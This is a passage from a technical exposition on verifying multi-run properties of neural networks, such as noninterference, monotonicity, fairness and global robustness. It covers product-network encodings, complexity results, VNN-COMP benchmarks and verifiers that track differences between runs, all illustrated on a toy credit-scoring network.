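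If it takes k runs to show that a network violates a requirement, checking that requirement takes k copies of the network. The one-bit leakage limit described in the previous section therefore needs three copies, all given the same public input.

### Noninterference as equivalence of two networks

We can tie the inputs together in the wiring instead of adding equations. Wurm does this to show that noninterference is a special case of a more familiar question, whether two networks compute the same function.

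Let N take a public part x_P and a secret part s. Define two networks on a longer input, which contains one public part and two secret parts:

N₁(x_P, s, s′) = N(x_P, s)

N₂(x_P, s, s′) = N(x_P, s′).

N₁ and N₂ both keep the weights of N and differ only in that N₁ ignores the secret s′ and N₂ ignores the secret s. For the toy lender, N₁(x, s, s′) is f(x, s) and N₂(x, s, s′) is f(x, s′). Two networks are equivalent if they give the same output on every input. The inputs to N₁ and N₂ cover every combination of one public part and two secrets, so the two networks are equivalent exactly when N satisfies noninterference.

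The rewiring takes time proportional to the size of the network and works for any activation function. With it, any tool that checks whether two networks are equivalent, such as one that engineers use to compare a compressed network with the original, can also check noninterference. Wurm warns that writing the software to duplicate the network and tie the public inputs together takes real work, even though the solver needs no change.

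Wurm's definition covers all real inputs, whereas the toy lender has x in [0, 2] and s in [0, 1]. A network may ignore s inside that box but depend on it outside. To restrict an equivalence check to a box, we can first apply the clip operation from the previous section, which moves every input into the box, and then apply N. Clip can output every point of the box, so N with clip in front satisfies noninterference everywhere exactly when N satisfies it on the box.

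### Replacing one secret by a fixed value

Equality is transitive, so it's enough to compare every secret with a single reference value r. Suppose that

N(x_P, s) = N(x_P, r) for every x_P and every s.

If N(x_P, s) = N(x_P, r) for every public input x_P and every secret s, where r is a fixed secret, then any two secrets s and s′ give the same output, because both outputs equal N(x_P, r). The second copy therefore needs no free secret, and r can be absorbed into its biases. For a network with 10 public and 200 secret inputs, the product then has 210 free inputs instead of 410.

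For the toy lender, take r = 0. The reference copy is then f(x, 0) = ReLU(x − 1) − ReLU(x − 1), which is 0 for every x, so the question about two runs becomes whether a single run of f can ever give a nonzero output. This does not contradict the earlier argument that no rule about single runs can define such a requirement, because the rule "the output is 0" depends on what this lender's reference copy computes, and another network would need another rule. In general, the reference copy stays in the product network, and the verifier has to reason about it too.

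Fixing one copy's secret at r breaks the symmetry between the copies, so we have to check both whether the first copy's output can be greater than the second's and whether it can be less. The value r should also be possible for every public part in the domain. Otherwise, a proof is still valid, but a counterexample may involve an input that could never occur.

The most important limit concerns tolerances. People often want the output to depend on the secret by at most δ, rather than not at all. If every N(x_P, s) is within δ of N(x_P, r), the triangle inequality gives only

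|N(x_P, s) − N(x_P, s′)| ≤ 2δ.

To guarantee that any two outputs differ by at most δ, we therefore have to prove that every output is within δ/2 of the reference, and a network that meets the original requirement may fail this stricter test. The toy lender's scores for the same x differ by at most 1. With r = 0, some scores are 1 away from the reference, so the trick guarantees only a limit of 2. With r = 0.5, every score is within 0.5 of the reference, so the trick recovers the exact limit of 1. A good reference lies in the middle of the outputs, which is easy to find here but can change with x_P in a larger network. Letting both secrets vary avoids this loss but requires a larger search.

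Equality of classes is transitive too, provided that each input has exactly one class. So to check attribute-flip fairness for a protected attribute with five values, we can compare four of them with the fifth instead of checking all ten pairs. Without a rule for breaking ties, this can fail, because an applicant tied between classes 1 and 2 would match both an applicant in class 1 and one in class 2.

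### Saying that two classes differ

When the outputs are scores, step 3 simply compares numbers. When they are decisions, it has to state that the two copies choose different classes. The class is the *position* of the largest score, and many verifiers cannot refer to a position. Marabou, which Athavale and colleagues use, accepts linear equations and inequalities, ReLU, maximum, absolute value and a limited form of "or", but not "is not equal to".

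They solve this by splitting the question into one case per label. For label i, the query asks for a pair of inputs with

max(y₁, …, yₙ) − yᵢ = 0  and  max(y′₁, …, y′ₙ) − y′ᵢ ≠ 0.

The equation means that label i has the top score in the first copy, and the second condition means that label i does not have the top score in the second copy. If none of the n queries has a solution, no pair of inputs gets different classes. In the actual method, the first copy's confidence must also exceed a threshold.

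To replace ≠, Athavale and colleagues check "less than 0" and "greater than 0" separately. A value less than 0 is impossible, because a maximum is at least as large as each of its entries, so one check per label would be enough. The linear constraints that the paper lists for Marabou use only ≤, ≥ and =, so "greater than 0" has to become something like "at least 0.0001". A proof then doesn't cover pairs in which label i scores below the winning label by less than that margin.

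We can also avoid the maximum by fixing a label for each copy. For labels i and j, the query requires yᵢ to be at least as large as every score in the first copy, and y′ⱼ to be at least as large as every score in the second. All the conditions are now non-strict linear inequalities, so we don't have to choose a margin. A tie may cause a false alarm, but the queries don't miss any real disagreement. This method takes more queries, one for each ordered pair of different labels. Ten classes need 90, or 45 if swapping the copies leaves the input condition unchanged.

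With two classes, one query is enough. The toy lender approves when f is at least 0.5, so a disagreement is a solution of

f(x, s) ≥ 0.5 and f(x, s′) < 0.5.

No solution exists for applicants with x of at most 0.4. In that range, ReLU(x − 1) is 0 and x + s − 1 is at most x, so f never exceeds 0.4 and the lender refuses everyone. When x is at least 0.5, s = 1 and s′ = 0 always give a solution.

Boetius and Leue's network Sat instead combines all the cases into a single number. For each label j, it takes the smallest of the differences yⱼ − yₖ and y′ⱼ − y′ₖ over all labels k, and then it takes the largest of these results over all j. The number is at least 0 exactly when some label has a top score in both copies.

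As written, the formula includes k = j, which always contributes a difference of 0. The number can then never exceed 0, even when both copies agree by a wide margin, so the verifier has to prove a lower bound of exactly 0, with no room for rounding error. Leaving out k = j solves this by making the number positive when the copies clearly agree. With ten classes, each label has 18 differences. Computing the minima and maxima pairwise, with one ReLU per pair, adds 10 × 17 + 9 = 179 ReLUs to the product network. One can either run many queries on the plain product network, which can run in parallel, or run one query on a larger network.

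In VNN-LIB 2.0, the grammar that Roy and colleagues define includes both "or" and "!=", so users can write all the cases in one query. Noninterference for the toy lender needs only two assertions beyond the ranges of the inputs:

```
(assert (== V[0] U[0]))
(assert (!= Z[0] Y[0]))
```

The solver still has to work through the cases internally, but users no longer have to split them by hand.

### "There is a run" inside "for all runs"

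Step 4 has the same limit as a VNN-LIB 2.0 query. A requirement of the form "for every run there is another run" fails when some run has no suitable partner. The verifier can find a fixed number of runs, but it cannot establish that no suitable partner exists.

Wurm's output indistinguishability has this form. It takes two sets of inputs, A₁ and A₂, for instance applicants from two groups, and requires

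for all x in A₁ there is x′ in A₂ such that N(x) and N(x′) are within δ of each other,

and the same with the sets exchanged. Wurm proposes it because exact noninterference is too brittle for trained networks. If the secret correlates with anything in the training data, the network will usually depend on it slightly and fail. But a tolerance alone does not require "there is". The rule that N(x_P, s) and N(x_P, s′) differ by at most δ is still about all pairs, and the product network can check it by looking for a larger difference. Output indistinguishability is for a different situation, in which an observer sees only the output and tries to tell which set the input came from.

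Here is an example where the product network gives the wrong answer:

h(x, s) = |x − 2s|, with x in [0, 2] and s equal to 0 or 1.

The score is x in group 0 and 2 − x in group 1. Both groups can receive every score from 0 to 2, so output indistinguishability holds even for δ = 0. If we join two copies and ask for one applicant from each group with different scores, the verifier will find a pair, such as x = 0 in both groups, with scores 0 and 2. This pair doesn't violate the property, because the applicant with x = 2 in group 1 also scores 0, matching the applicant in group 0.

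One way around this is to choose the partner ourselves. HypRL replaced "there is a path" with a function, and the same step works here. If w(x) = 2 − x picks the partner in group 1, the difference between the scores is

h(x, 0) − h(2 − x, 1) = x − x = 0,

and a verifier can prove this with an ordinary query about one free number. The same w works in the other direction. Had we chosen w(x) = x, the difference would have been 2x − 2, and the check would have failed although the requirement holds. A successful check therefore proves the requirement however we found w, but a failed one may only mean that we picked the wrong function.

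If there are only a few possible partners, we can give each one its own copy of the network. An ordinary query can then express "there is a partner that matches" as "the first matches, or the second matches", and so on. Wurm concludes that current verifiers cannot handle the question directly when partners range over a continuum, as in output indistinguishability.

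## How much harder is checking two runs than checking one?

A product network has about twice as many neurons as the original. This doubling doesn't change the problem's complexity class, a broad category based on how fast the worst case grows. For ReLU networks, checking noninterference, monotonicity or attribute-flip fairness is in the same class as ordinary verification. In practice, a verifier can still take the square of the time, so a check that takes minutes for one run may take decades for two.

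### Two runs stay in the same complexity class

Ordinary verification of ReLU networks is already hard. Suppose linear inequalities describe a set of allowed inputs and a set of forbidden outputs, and we ask whether any allowed input produces a forbidden output. *The Complexity of Verifying Feedforward Neural Networks in Quantised Settings* (Alsmann, Lange and Sälzer, 2026) reviews the proof that this question is NP-complete. NP contains the problems whose "yes" answers have short proofs that a computer can check quickly, and the NP-complete problems are the hardest of these. Nobody knows a fast algorithm for them, and most researchers doubt that one exists. To certify a network, a verifier must establish that no allowed input produces a forbidden output, which is a co-NP-complete problem.

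An activation pattern, which records whether each ReLU is on or off, is a short proof that a bad input exists. Anyone can check it in three steps.

1. Replace each ReLU that is on by its weighted sum, and each ReLU that is off by 0. The network is now linear.
2. Collect the inequalities for the allowed inputs and the forbidden outputs, and add one per ReLU to make sure that its weighted sum really has the sign that the pattern claims.
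3. Solve the resulting linear program, which takes polynomial time (time that grows no faster than a fixed power of the problem's size).

A pair of runs needs two patterns, one for each copy of the network, and still only one linear program. Take noninterference for the toy lender, f(x, s) = ReLU(x + s − 1) − ReLU(x − 1). Suppose that in the first copy only the first ReLU is on, and in the second copy both are off. The outputs are then x + s − 1 and 0, and the pattern requires

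x + s − 1 ≥ 0,  x − 1 ≤ 0,  x + s′ − 1 ≤ 0.

The largest difference under these inequalities is 1, at x = 1, s = 1 and s′ = 0, which is the counterexample pair from before.

In a single-author preprint from September 2026, Wurm derives the general result from a theorem about logic. He discloses that a large language model suggested some formal definitions and drafted some arguments, and that he checked every proof himself. The arguments about two runs are short enough to work through by hand.

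His first step is to write the network as a formula. A ReLU with weighted sum z and output y satisfies

(z ≥ 0 and y = z) or (z ≤ 0 and y = 0).

Joining one such condition per neuron with "and" gives a formula whose length is proportional to the size of the network. The formula adds variables and multiplies them by constants, but never multiplies two variables together. In 1985, Eduardo Sontag showed that the difficulty of deciding such statements depends on how often their quantifiers switch between "for all" and "there is". A statement that uses only "for all" is in co-NP. Each switch moves the problem up one level in the polynomial hierarchy, a sequence of complexity classes with NP and co-NP at its first level. Most researchers believe that each level is harder than the one below.

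The definition of noninterference begins "for all u, for all u′". Both quantifiers are universal, so they count as one block. The second copy of the network doubles the length of the formula but adds no quantifier alternation, so the problem stays in co-NP. The same reasoning covers monotonicity, attribute-flip fairness and any k-safety requirement that linear inequalities can express, as long as k is fixed.

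It also covers a privacy question. Suppose a company publishes a score and wants to know whether two very different people could have received it. Wurm's version is to decide whether all inputs whose outputs fall in a given region lie within a distance δ of each other, and he proves that this is co-NP-complete too.

### A network built from a logic puzzle

Membership in co-NP gives only an upper bound on the difficulty. To show that two-run requirements are as hard as any problem in the class, Wurm turns 3-SAT puzzles into networks. A 3-SAT puzzle consists of clauses such as "p or q or not r", and the task is to decide whether some choice of true and false for the variables satisfies every clause. This problem is NP-complete.

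The network has one input per variable, where 1 means true and 0 means false. For a variable p with input z, it computes two values:

P = 2 ReLU(z − ½) − 2 ReLU(z − 1),  P̄ = 2 ReLU(½ − z) − 2 ReLU(−z).

P is 1 when z = 1 and 0 when z = 0, and P̄ is the reverse. For each clause, the network adds the values of the three terms and caps the sum at 1. Adding up the clauses gives M(z), the number of satisfied clauses whenever all inputs are 0 or 1. With m clauses in total, the final output is

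g(z) = ReLU(M(z) − (m − 1)),

which is 1 if all the clauses are satisfied and 0 if at least one is not.

The inputs can also lie between 0 and 1, so a clause might be only partly satisfied. Wurm rules this out by rounding every input to 0 or 1, with ½ going to 0. If a clause is false after rounding, all three of its terms were 0 before rounding, so it contributed nothing to M. Therefore g is 0 everywhere exactly when no true-or-false assignment solves the puzzle.

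The smallest unsolvable puzzle has two clauses, "p or p or p" and "not p or not p or not p". P and P̄ are never both positive, so M is at most 1, and g = ReLU(M − 1) is always 0. If we drop the second clause, g rises from 0 at z = ½ to 1 at z = ⅔.

The step to monotonicity needs one more input t between 0 and 1:

h(z, t) = ReLU(g(z) − t).

If the puzzle has no solution, h is 0 everywhere, so it never falls. If the puzzle has a solution, some z gives g(z) = 1, and raising t from 0 to 1 lowers h from 1 to 0. A verifier that can decide whether h is monotone in t can therefore decide whether any 3-SAT puzzle has a solution. Comparing t = 0 with t = 1 is trivial once we have z, so the only hard part is finding z, which is a question about single runs.

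If we declare all the inputs of g secret, noninterference means that g is constant. Since g is always 0 when every input is ½, it is constant exactly when the puzzle has no solution.

For attribute-flip fairness, let t be the protected attribute, which a flip changes to 1 − t. The network gives class 1 a score of 1 and class 2 a score of 2 − 2 ReLU(g(z) + t − 1). If g is 0 everywhere, class 2 always scores 2, so the network always chooses it. If g(z) = 1 for some z, then at that z class 2 scores 2 when t = 0 but 0 when t = 1, so the flip changes the decision.

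The monotonicity result appeared before the preprint, in Wurm's *Checking extracted rules in Neural Networks* (2025), which showed that checking monotonicity rules on ReLU networks is co-NP-complete. The paper covers a broader kind of rule, in which a matrix determines when one input counts as larger than another. Its proof also runs two copies of the network in parallel. The hardness argument shows that an unsolvable puzzle produces a constant network, which is monotone, but does not explain how a solvable puzzle produces a non-monotone one. Subtracting t, as above, supplies the missing step.

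A worst-case result about networks that encode logic puzzles does not show whether a particular credit model is hard to check. But the hard cases are not limited to carefully chosen weights. Wurm cites a 2026 result by Mojtaba Soltanalian, who adds random noise to every weight and bias. Even then, no sound and complete verifier can be fast on average unless randomised algorithms can solve every problem in NP quickly.

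### Where the class does change

Output indistinguishability, which Wurm considers more useful than exact noninterference, requires that for every input from one group there is an input from the other with nearly the same output. The switch from "for all" to "there is" puts the problem on the second level of the hierarchy, though this is again only an upper limit. Wurm conjectures that it is as hard as any problem on that level but has not proved this.

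He does have a proof for a related question about backdoors. A backdoored image classifier behaves normally except on images with a certain small patch, which it always assigns to the attacker's class. Checking for a backdoor means deciding whether some patch produces that class when added to any image. If each pixel of the patch comes from a finite list of values, this problem is complete for the second level of the polynomial hierarchy, so no polynomial-time method can always solve it using calls to an ordinary verifier, unless the levels of the hierarchy turn out to be the same.

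The proof fails if the patch's pixels can take any real value. In the puzzle network, an input of ½ makes both P and P̄ zero, so the variable is neither true nor false. An attacker could use such a value to leave clauses unsatisfied that any true-or-false assignment would satisfy. It is an open question whether the continuous problem is easier, and the same difficulty is also an obstacle to a proof for output indistinguishability.

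Other activation functions change the complexity class for a different reason. The sigmoid, 1/(1 + e⁻ᶻ), is a smooth curve, so no formula with only linear pieces can describe it exactly. According to Wurm, checking noninterference, monotonicity or attribute-flip fairness on networks with sigmoids is ∀ℝ-hard, meaning at least as hard as deciding whether a statement about sums and products holds for all real numbers. Researchers believe this is harder than anything in co-NP. Wurm states the result in remarks, without writing out the puzzle network for the sigmoid. Questions about single runs of sigmoid networks are already ∀ℝ-hard, so the added difficulty again doesn't come from the second run.

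Products also appear when the weights are uncertain, for example because a chip stores them imprecisely. An unknown weight then multiplies an unknown value, so the formula is no longer linear. Wurm proves that deciding whether some fault leads to a forbidden output is complete for ∃ℝ, the "there is" counterpart of ∀ℝ. This holds even for networks with no nonlinear functions and for very small tolerances. The proof requires some weights to appear in two places in the network, as they do in convolutional layers. The case where every weight appears only once is open.

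Real computers also round numbers, so results for exact arithmetic may be misleading. Alsmann and colleagues examined this for single runs and found that if a network's weights already use a fixed number format, verification with linear inequalities is NP-complete, just as in exact arithmetic. It remains NP-complete if the requirement can refer to individual bits. *Scalable Verification of Quantized Neural Networks (Technical Report)* (2020) proves that the problem becomes PSPACE-hard when the network is given in full precision, the number format is chosen separately, and the requirement is stated in terms of bits. PSPACE is the class of problems that a computer can solve with a polynomial amount of memory, and it contains the whole polynomial hierarchy.

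Alsmann and colleagues argue that people have misread this proof as showing that rounding makes verification harder. They attribute the added difficulty to the richer language for requirements. Their own results suggest a second cause, because the richer language doesn't make verification harder when the format is fixed. Separately chosen formats may matter because a few digits can specify a format with a huge number of bits.

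Checking group fairness can require counting. Equal approval rates, for example, depend on the proportion of people a network approves in each group, so no single counterexample can settle the question. Wurm expects such questions to be complete for #P, the class of problems about how many solutions exist, but nobody has proved this for the ReLU networks and properties he considers.

### Systems that run for many steps

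For systems that act over time, the corresponding question is whether a system satisfies a HyperLTL formula. Finkbeiner's *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (2025) surveys how hard this is to check for systems with finitely many states. The basic algorithm, which he published with Rabe and Sánchez in 2015, first negates the formula so that it describes an error. It then searches for runs that fit the description, using one copy of the system for each quantifier (*Model Checking Quantitative Hyperproperties*, 2019).

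The search relies on an automaton, a simple machine that reads runs step by step and accepts or rejects them. For each switch between "for all" and "there is", the algorithm must build an automaton that accepts exactly what the previous one rejected, and the new automaton can be exponentially larger. Checking a formula without switches, such as observational determinism, takes memory proportional to the logarithm of the number of states. Checking generalised noninterference, which has one switch, takes polynomial memory. Each further switch increases the memory needed exponentially. Checking is much easier if the system never returns to an earlier state, and a tree-shaped system needs only logarithmic memory however many switches there are.

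*AutoHyper* (2023) tested its tool on randomly generated formulas with one to four switches. The running time rose with each switch, but by much less than the theory allows. Random formulas may be easier to check than the ones people care about.

These complexity results are hard to compare with those for neural networks, because they depend on the number of states. In 32-bit arithmetic, the toy lender's x and s can each take more than a billion values, so it has more than a quintillion inputs. An algorithm that visits states one by one would take impractically long, even though the network has only two ReLUs. Neural network verifiers instead work with whole regions of inputs at a time.

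A formula can also be impossible for any system to satisfy, so verification always fails. Finkbeiner reports that no algorithm can detect this for every formula that has "there is" inside "for all". For formulas with only one kind of quantifier, detecting this is exactly as hard as for LTL.

### Squaring the number of activation patterns

A complete verifier for ReLU networks has to account for every activation pattern that can occur. It usually begins by computing a range for each neuron's weighted sum. If the range contains only positive or only negative numbers, the ReLU is always on or always off, and the verifier can treat it as linear. Otherwise, the ReLU is undecided, and u undecided ReLUs allow up to 2ᵘ patterns.

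In the toy lender, the difficulty of verification depends on the domain. Within 0.1 of the input (1.5, 0.5), the two weighted sums lie between 0.8 and 1.2 and between 0.4 and 0.6, so both ReLUs are on and the network returns s. Over the whole domain, the sums range from −1 to 2 and from −1 to 1, so both ReLUs are undecided. A global requirement therefore makes verification harder even before we add the second copy.

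Two copies have four undecided ReLUs, so there are up to 16 on/off patterns. For noninterference, the copies share x, so ReLU(x − 1) is the same in both and the number falls to 8. Only five of these can occur, because when x is greater than 1, the other two ReLUs must also be on.

Larger networks have far more patterns. One copy with 20 undecided ReLUs has up to about a million patterns, while two copies have 40 undecided ReLUs and up to about a trillion patterns. A computer that solves a thousand linear programs per second would get through the million in 17 minutes and the trillion in 35 years. Checking the limit on one-bit leaks takes three copies, which have up to 2⁶⁰ patterns, about a quintillion. All of these problems are in co-NP, because squaring 2ᵘ does not move a problem out of that class.

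The number of activation patterns can be much lower when the network has few inputs. In a network with two inputs and one hidden layer of 20 ReLUs, each ReLU switches on or off along a line in the plane, and 20 lines divide a plane into at most 211 regions. One copy therefore has at most 211 patterns, and two copies with independent inputs have up to 211², or 44,521.

For networks with few inputs, a verifier can also divide the domain into small boxes and check them one at a time. *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) describes a tool, PyRAT, that can split the inputs on small problems and the ReLUs on larger networks. Checking two runs can also square the number of boxes. If a network has five inputs and we cut each range into ten parts, one run needs 100,000 boxes. Monotonicity adds one input, so it needs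 a million boxes. Global robustness lets all five inputs vary in both runs, so it needs ten inputs and ten billion boxes.

The number of neurons alone is a poor guide to difficulty. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) lists a set of test problems made with Relusplitter, a program that rewrites the network in an existing problem so that ReLUs that were always on or always off become undecided. The rewritten network computes the same function but is harder to verify, and the researchers who proposed the set tripled the time limit for such networks.

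Good verifiers rarely have to check every pattern, because they compute bounds that eliminate many patterns at once and split only the ReLUs that still matter. Newer methods also bound the difference between the two copies' values, which is often much smaller than the range of values in either copy.

### The sizes that ordinary verifiers face

VNN-COMP, the annual competition for neural network verification tools, gives a baseline for checking single runs. Each problem consists of a network, a requirement and a time limit, and the limits for one set of problems can total at most six hours. A tool earns 10 points for each correct answer, whether it proves the requirement or finds a counterexample, and loses 150 for each wrong one. The 2026 report ranks 13 tools, up from seven in 2025, and α,β-CROWN won in both years.

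The table shows some of the 2026 problems, with the sizes that the competition set. A tool can still run out of time on any of them.

| Problem set | Network | Inputs that vary | Domain |
|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu, collision advice for aircraft | 300 ReLUs | 5 | part of the possible flight states |
| cersyve, safety certificates for controllers | 1,000 to 4,000 parameters | 2 to 6 | every possible state |
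| TLL, networks with a special lattice structure | 17,000 to 67 million parameters, many of them zero | 2 | a whole square |
| safeNLP, classification of sentences | 4,000 parameters | 30 | a box around variants of one sentence |
| VGG-16, classification of photographs | 138 million parameters | 1 to 150,528 | small changes to one photograph |

The image classifier is very large, but its domain only surrounds a single photograph. The networks that tools must verify over an entire domain have at most six inputs. The cersyve paper notes that most other problems cover only a small region around known data or part of the possible states. Proving global robustness for an image classifier would require a large network, a large domain and a second copy of the network.

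The competition also includes logic puzzles like Wurm's. One set encodes 100 random 3-SAT puzzles as ReLU networks. The puzzles have 2 to 100 variables, and half are solvable. The correct answers are known in advance, so the set can reveal verifiers' mistakes.

At least one benchmark set, NN4Sys, compares runs. Its 11 networks do jobs inside computer systems. Four estimate how many rows a database query will return, and five choose the quality of a video stream. Some requirements for these nine networks are for monotonicity between two inputs, meaning the larger input must produce the larger output. A set from Collins Aerospace also includes monotonicity, for networks that predict how long a machine part will last, but only around a given input. That input is fixed and its output is known, so the check involves a single run.

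The file format is becoming less of an obstacle to such comparisons. In 2026, every problem set in the competition's main track came with a version in VNN-LIB 2.0, which can describe several runs. Ladner and colleagues report that the tools could read most of these files and used the older format when a file contained something they didn't support. The organisers want to use only the new format in 2027.

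Rounding matters more when a property requires exact equality between two runs. Under the 2026 rules, a counterexample counts fully only if its inputs meet the stated conditions exactly, and the organisers compute its outputs with a standard program. The earlier network g(x, s) = ReLU(x + s) − ReLU(s) satisfies noninterference in exact arithmetic but not in 32-bit arithmetic. If the competition included this problem, a tool that reasons about exact real numbers would certify the network. Another tool could then submit two inputs that differ only in s but give different outputs because of rounding, and the first tool would lose 150 points.

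## Why do newer verifiers track the difference between runs?

A verifier can compute the range of possible outputs for each copy of a network separately and then compare the two ranges. This ignores the most useful fact about the two runs, that their inputs are close together or mostly the same.

Take the toy lender with s fixed at 1:

f(x, 1) = ReLU(x) − ReLU(x − 1), with x in [0, 2].

Two applicants have values x and x′ that differ by at most 0.1, and we want to know how far apart their scores can be.

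Computing a separate range for each applicant's score gives a loose bound on the difference between them. ReLU(x) lies between 0 and 2 and ReLU(x − 1) between 0 and 1, so the score lies between −1 and 2. The other applicant's score has the same range, so the bound on the difference is 3.

We get much closer by following the difference through the network. Each neuron's weighted sum changes by at most 0.1 from one run to the other. A ReLU never enlarges a difference, so each neuron's output also changes by at most 0.1. This limit on a single neuron is called a difference bound. The score is one neuron's output minus the other's, so it changes by at most 0.2.

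The true limit is 0.1, because f(x, 1) equals x up to x = 1 and stays at 1 after that. The estimate of 0.2 is too high because it lets one neuron rise while the other falls. But both depend on the same x, so they can only move in the same direction, and their changes partly cancel.

### A linear limit on the difference of two ReLUs

To keep track of such cancellation, a verifier needs a formula that links a neuron's difference after the ReLU to its difference before it. Let z be the weighted sum in the first run and z + d the weighted sum in the second. The difference after the ReLU is

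D = ReLU(z + d) − ReLU(z).

If the ReLU is on in both runs, D equals d. If it is off in both, D is 0 however large d is. For example, the sums −5 and −1 differ by 4, but the ReLU turns both into 0. If the ReLU is on in only one run, D lies between 0 and d. On a graph of D against d, the possible points therefore form two triangles that touch at the origin.

Linear programs need a region without such a pinch in the middle. If d lies between l and u, with l negative and u positive, Wang, Huang and Zhu (2022), in *Efficient Global Robustness Certification of Neural Networks via Interleaving Twin-Network Encoding*, replace the triangles with a parallelogram that contains both:

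l(u − d)/(u − l) ≤ D ≤ u(d − l)/(u − l).

Replacing an exact relationship with a looser linear one is called relaxation. All four corners of the parallelogram can occur, so no smaller convex region contains every possible point.

For the toy lender, l = −0.1 and u = 0.1, and the formula becomes

0.5d − 0.05 ≤ D ≤ 0.5d + 0.05.

Both neurons have the same d, since both sums change by x′ − x. The change in the score is therefore at most

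(0.5d + 0.05) − (0.5d − 0.05) = 0.1,

which is the exact answer. The terms in d cancel because the calculation keeps d as a symbol until the end and doesn't replace it with a range at every neuron.

### Linking the copies at every neuron

The early verifier Reluplex (2017) could check global robustness with two copies of a network, but it linked them only at the inputs and outputs. Wang and colleagues add two variables for every hidden neuron, one for the difference between its values in the two copies before the ReLU and one for the difference after it.

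Wang and colleagues illustrate the benefit of the difference variables with a small network that has two hidden neurons and two inputs between −1 and 1. If each input moves by up to 0.1, the output changes by at most 0.2. When they relaxed the two copies separately, the range they computed for this change was 10.9 times too wide. With the difference variables, it was 1.38 times too wide.

The full method saves time in two other ways. It computes each neuron's bounds from only the two or three layers before it, so it never has to solve the whole network at once. It also treats ReLUs exactly only for the neurons with the loosest relaxations. Each exact ReLU needs a yes-or-no variable, which makes the linear program a mixed-integer linear program (MILP), and the time to solve it can grow exponentially with the number of these variables.

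They compared their method with two exact ones, Reluplex and a MILP for the whole product network, on small networks that predict cars' fuel consumption. The table shows how long each method took to bound the change in the prediction when each input changes by 0.001.

| Hidden neurons | Reluplex | Exact MILP | Wang and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| 8 | 2 seconds | 0.1 seconds | 0.3 seconds |
| 16 | 8 hours | 0.8 seconds | 1 second |
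| 32 | over 24 hours | 74 seconds | 5 seconds |
| 64 | over 24 hours | over 24 hours | 50 seconds |

Their limit was 13% to 40% higher than the exact answer where one was available. They also tested three networks that recognise handwritten digits from the MNIST dataset, the largest with 5,824 hidden neurons according to their table. Each network took 3.3 to 4.8 hours. Nobody knows the exact answers for these networks, so they searched around the images in the dataset for the largest change they could find. The certified limits were 1.7 to 2.9 times as large as these changes, and the true values lie in between.

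They then used the method in a simulated car that keeps its distance from the car in front. A network estimates the distance from a small camera image. The method proved that if no pixel changes by more than 2/255 of its range, the estimate moves by at most 0.0568. The network's own error was at most 0.0730, so the total error is at most 0.1298. A separate analysis of the controller showed that the car stays safe as long as the error is below 0.14. In over 1,000 minutes of simulation with attacks of this size, the error never exceeded 0.14. With attacks of 10/255, about 17% of the simulations became unsafe.

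The safety proof still depends on a measured value, 0.0730, which is the largest error on the dataset. The error could be larger on other images.

### Using the state of each copy

The parallelogram is unnecessary when we know whether the ReLU is on or off in each run. RaVeN, a verifier from 2024, uses this fact. According to Fukuda and colleagues, it works layer by layer, computing linear bounds on the neurons in each copy and on the differences between copies, and uses those bounds to choose a formula for each neuron.

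| First run | Second run | Difference after the ReLU, second minus first |
|---|---|---|
| off | off | 0 |
| on | on | the difference before the ReLU |
| off | on | the second run's weighted sum |
| on | off | minus the first run's weighted sum |
| undecided | undecided | the parallelogram, or one triangle if the sign of d is known |

If the ReLU is undecided in only one run, RaVeN relaxes that copy and treats the other exactly.

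In the toy lender with s = 1, if both applicants have x of at least 1, both ReLUs are on in both runs, so each neuron's difference equals x′ − x and the scores are identical. If both applicants have x of at most 1, the second ReLU is off in both runs and contributes nothing to the difference in scores.

### One disturbance applied to many inputs

A smudge on a camera lens affects every picture in the same way. Attackers can do something similar with a universal adversarial perturbation, a single small change that makes a network misclassify many images. To prove that a network resists such attacks, a verifier has to consider all the images together, since the network may misclassify each image under some change even though no single change makes it misclassify them all.

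Banerjee and Singh (2024), in *Relational DNN Verification With Cross Executional Bound Refinement*, present a verifier for this problem called RACoon. Here is a simplified example of how it works. The disturbance is a single number δ between −1 and 1, and the margin of an image is the amount by which the correct class leads. Suppose we have proved that

margin of image A ≥ 0.5 + δ,  margin of image B ≥ 0.5 − δ.

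Image A may fail when δ is below −0.5, and image B may fail when δ is above 0.5, so we can't certify either one by checking them separately. But the lower limits on their margins average 0.5 for every δ. At least one margin is therefore always 0.5 or more, so no single disturbance can make the network misclassify both images.

In general, RACoon gives each image i a weight λᵢ, with the weights adding up to 1, and computes

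Σᵢ λᵢaᵢ − ε Σⱼ |Σᵢ λᵢLᵢⱼ|.

Here aᵢ is the limit on image i's margin without disturbance, Lᵢⱼ is how fast this limit changes with pixel j, and ε is the largest change allowed in any pixel. If the result is at least 0, no allowed disturbance fools the network on every image. The formula adds the images' weighted slopes before taking the absolute value, so slopes with opposite signs cancel. In the example, equal weights give 0.5 − 0 = 0.5, while putting all the weight on image A gives 0.5 − 1 = −0.5.

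The limits can also be adjusted. ReLU(z) is at least αz for any α between 0 and 1, so a verifier can choose a different α for each neuron. Existing tools choose these numbers to get the best limit for each image separately. RACoon uses gradient descent, the method that also trains neural networks, to choose them for all the images together, along with the weights. When Banerjee and Singh tested both approaches on four pairs of images, choosing α jointly ruled out a common disturbance for all four, while choosing it separately did so for none.

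They then tested RACoon on groups of 20 MNIST digits and groups of 10 photographs from CIFAR-10, a dataset of small colour images. They compared it with a 2023 verifier by Zeng and colleagues that links the runs only at the inputs. RACoon raised the guaranteed accuracy when the same disturbance was applied to every image in a group, by up to 16.5% on MNIST and up to 22% on CIFAR-10. For networks reading strings of 20 binary digits, it lowered the proved limit on the number of misread digits by up to 8. It was slower than Zeng's verifier but took less than 8 seconds for 20 MNIST images even on one of the larger networks. Banerjee and Singh say that it doesn't scale to networks trained on larger datasets such as ImageNet.

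RACoon links the runs through the disturbance they share, rather than computing differences neuron by neuron. It therefore needs less computation than RaVeN, which has to keep linear constraints for every layer and every run.

### Branch and bound

All the methods so far compute their bounds once, and if the bounds are too loose, they give no answer. Branch and bound continues from there:

1. Compute bounds. If they prove the requirement, stop.
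2. Otherwise, take the inputs that seem to break the requirement and run the real network on them. If they do break it, stop and report them.
3. If it was a false alarm, split the problem into two cases and start again with each.

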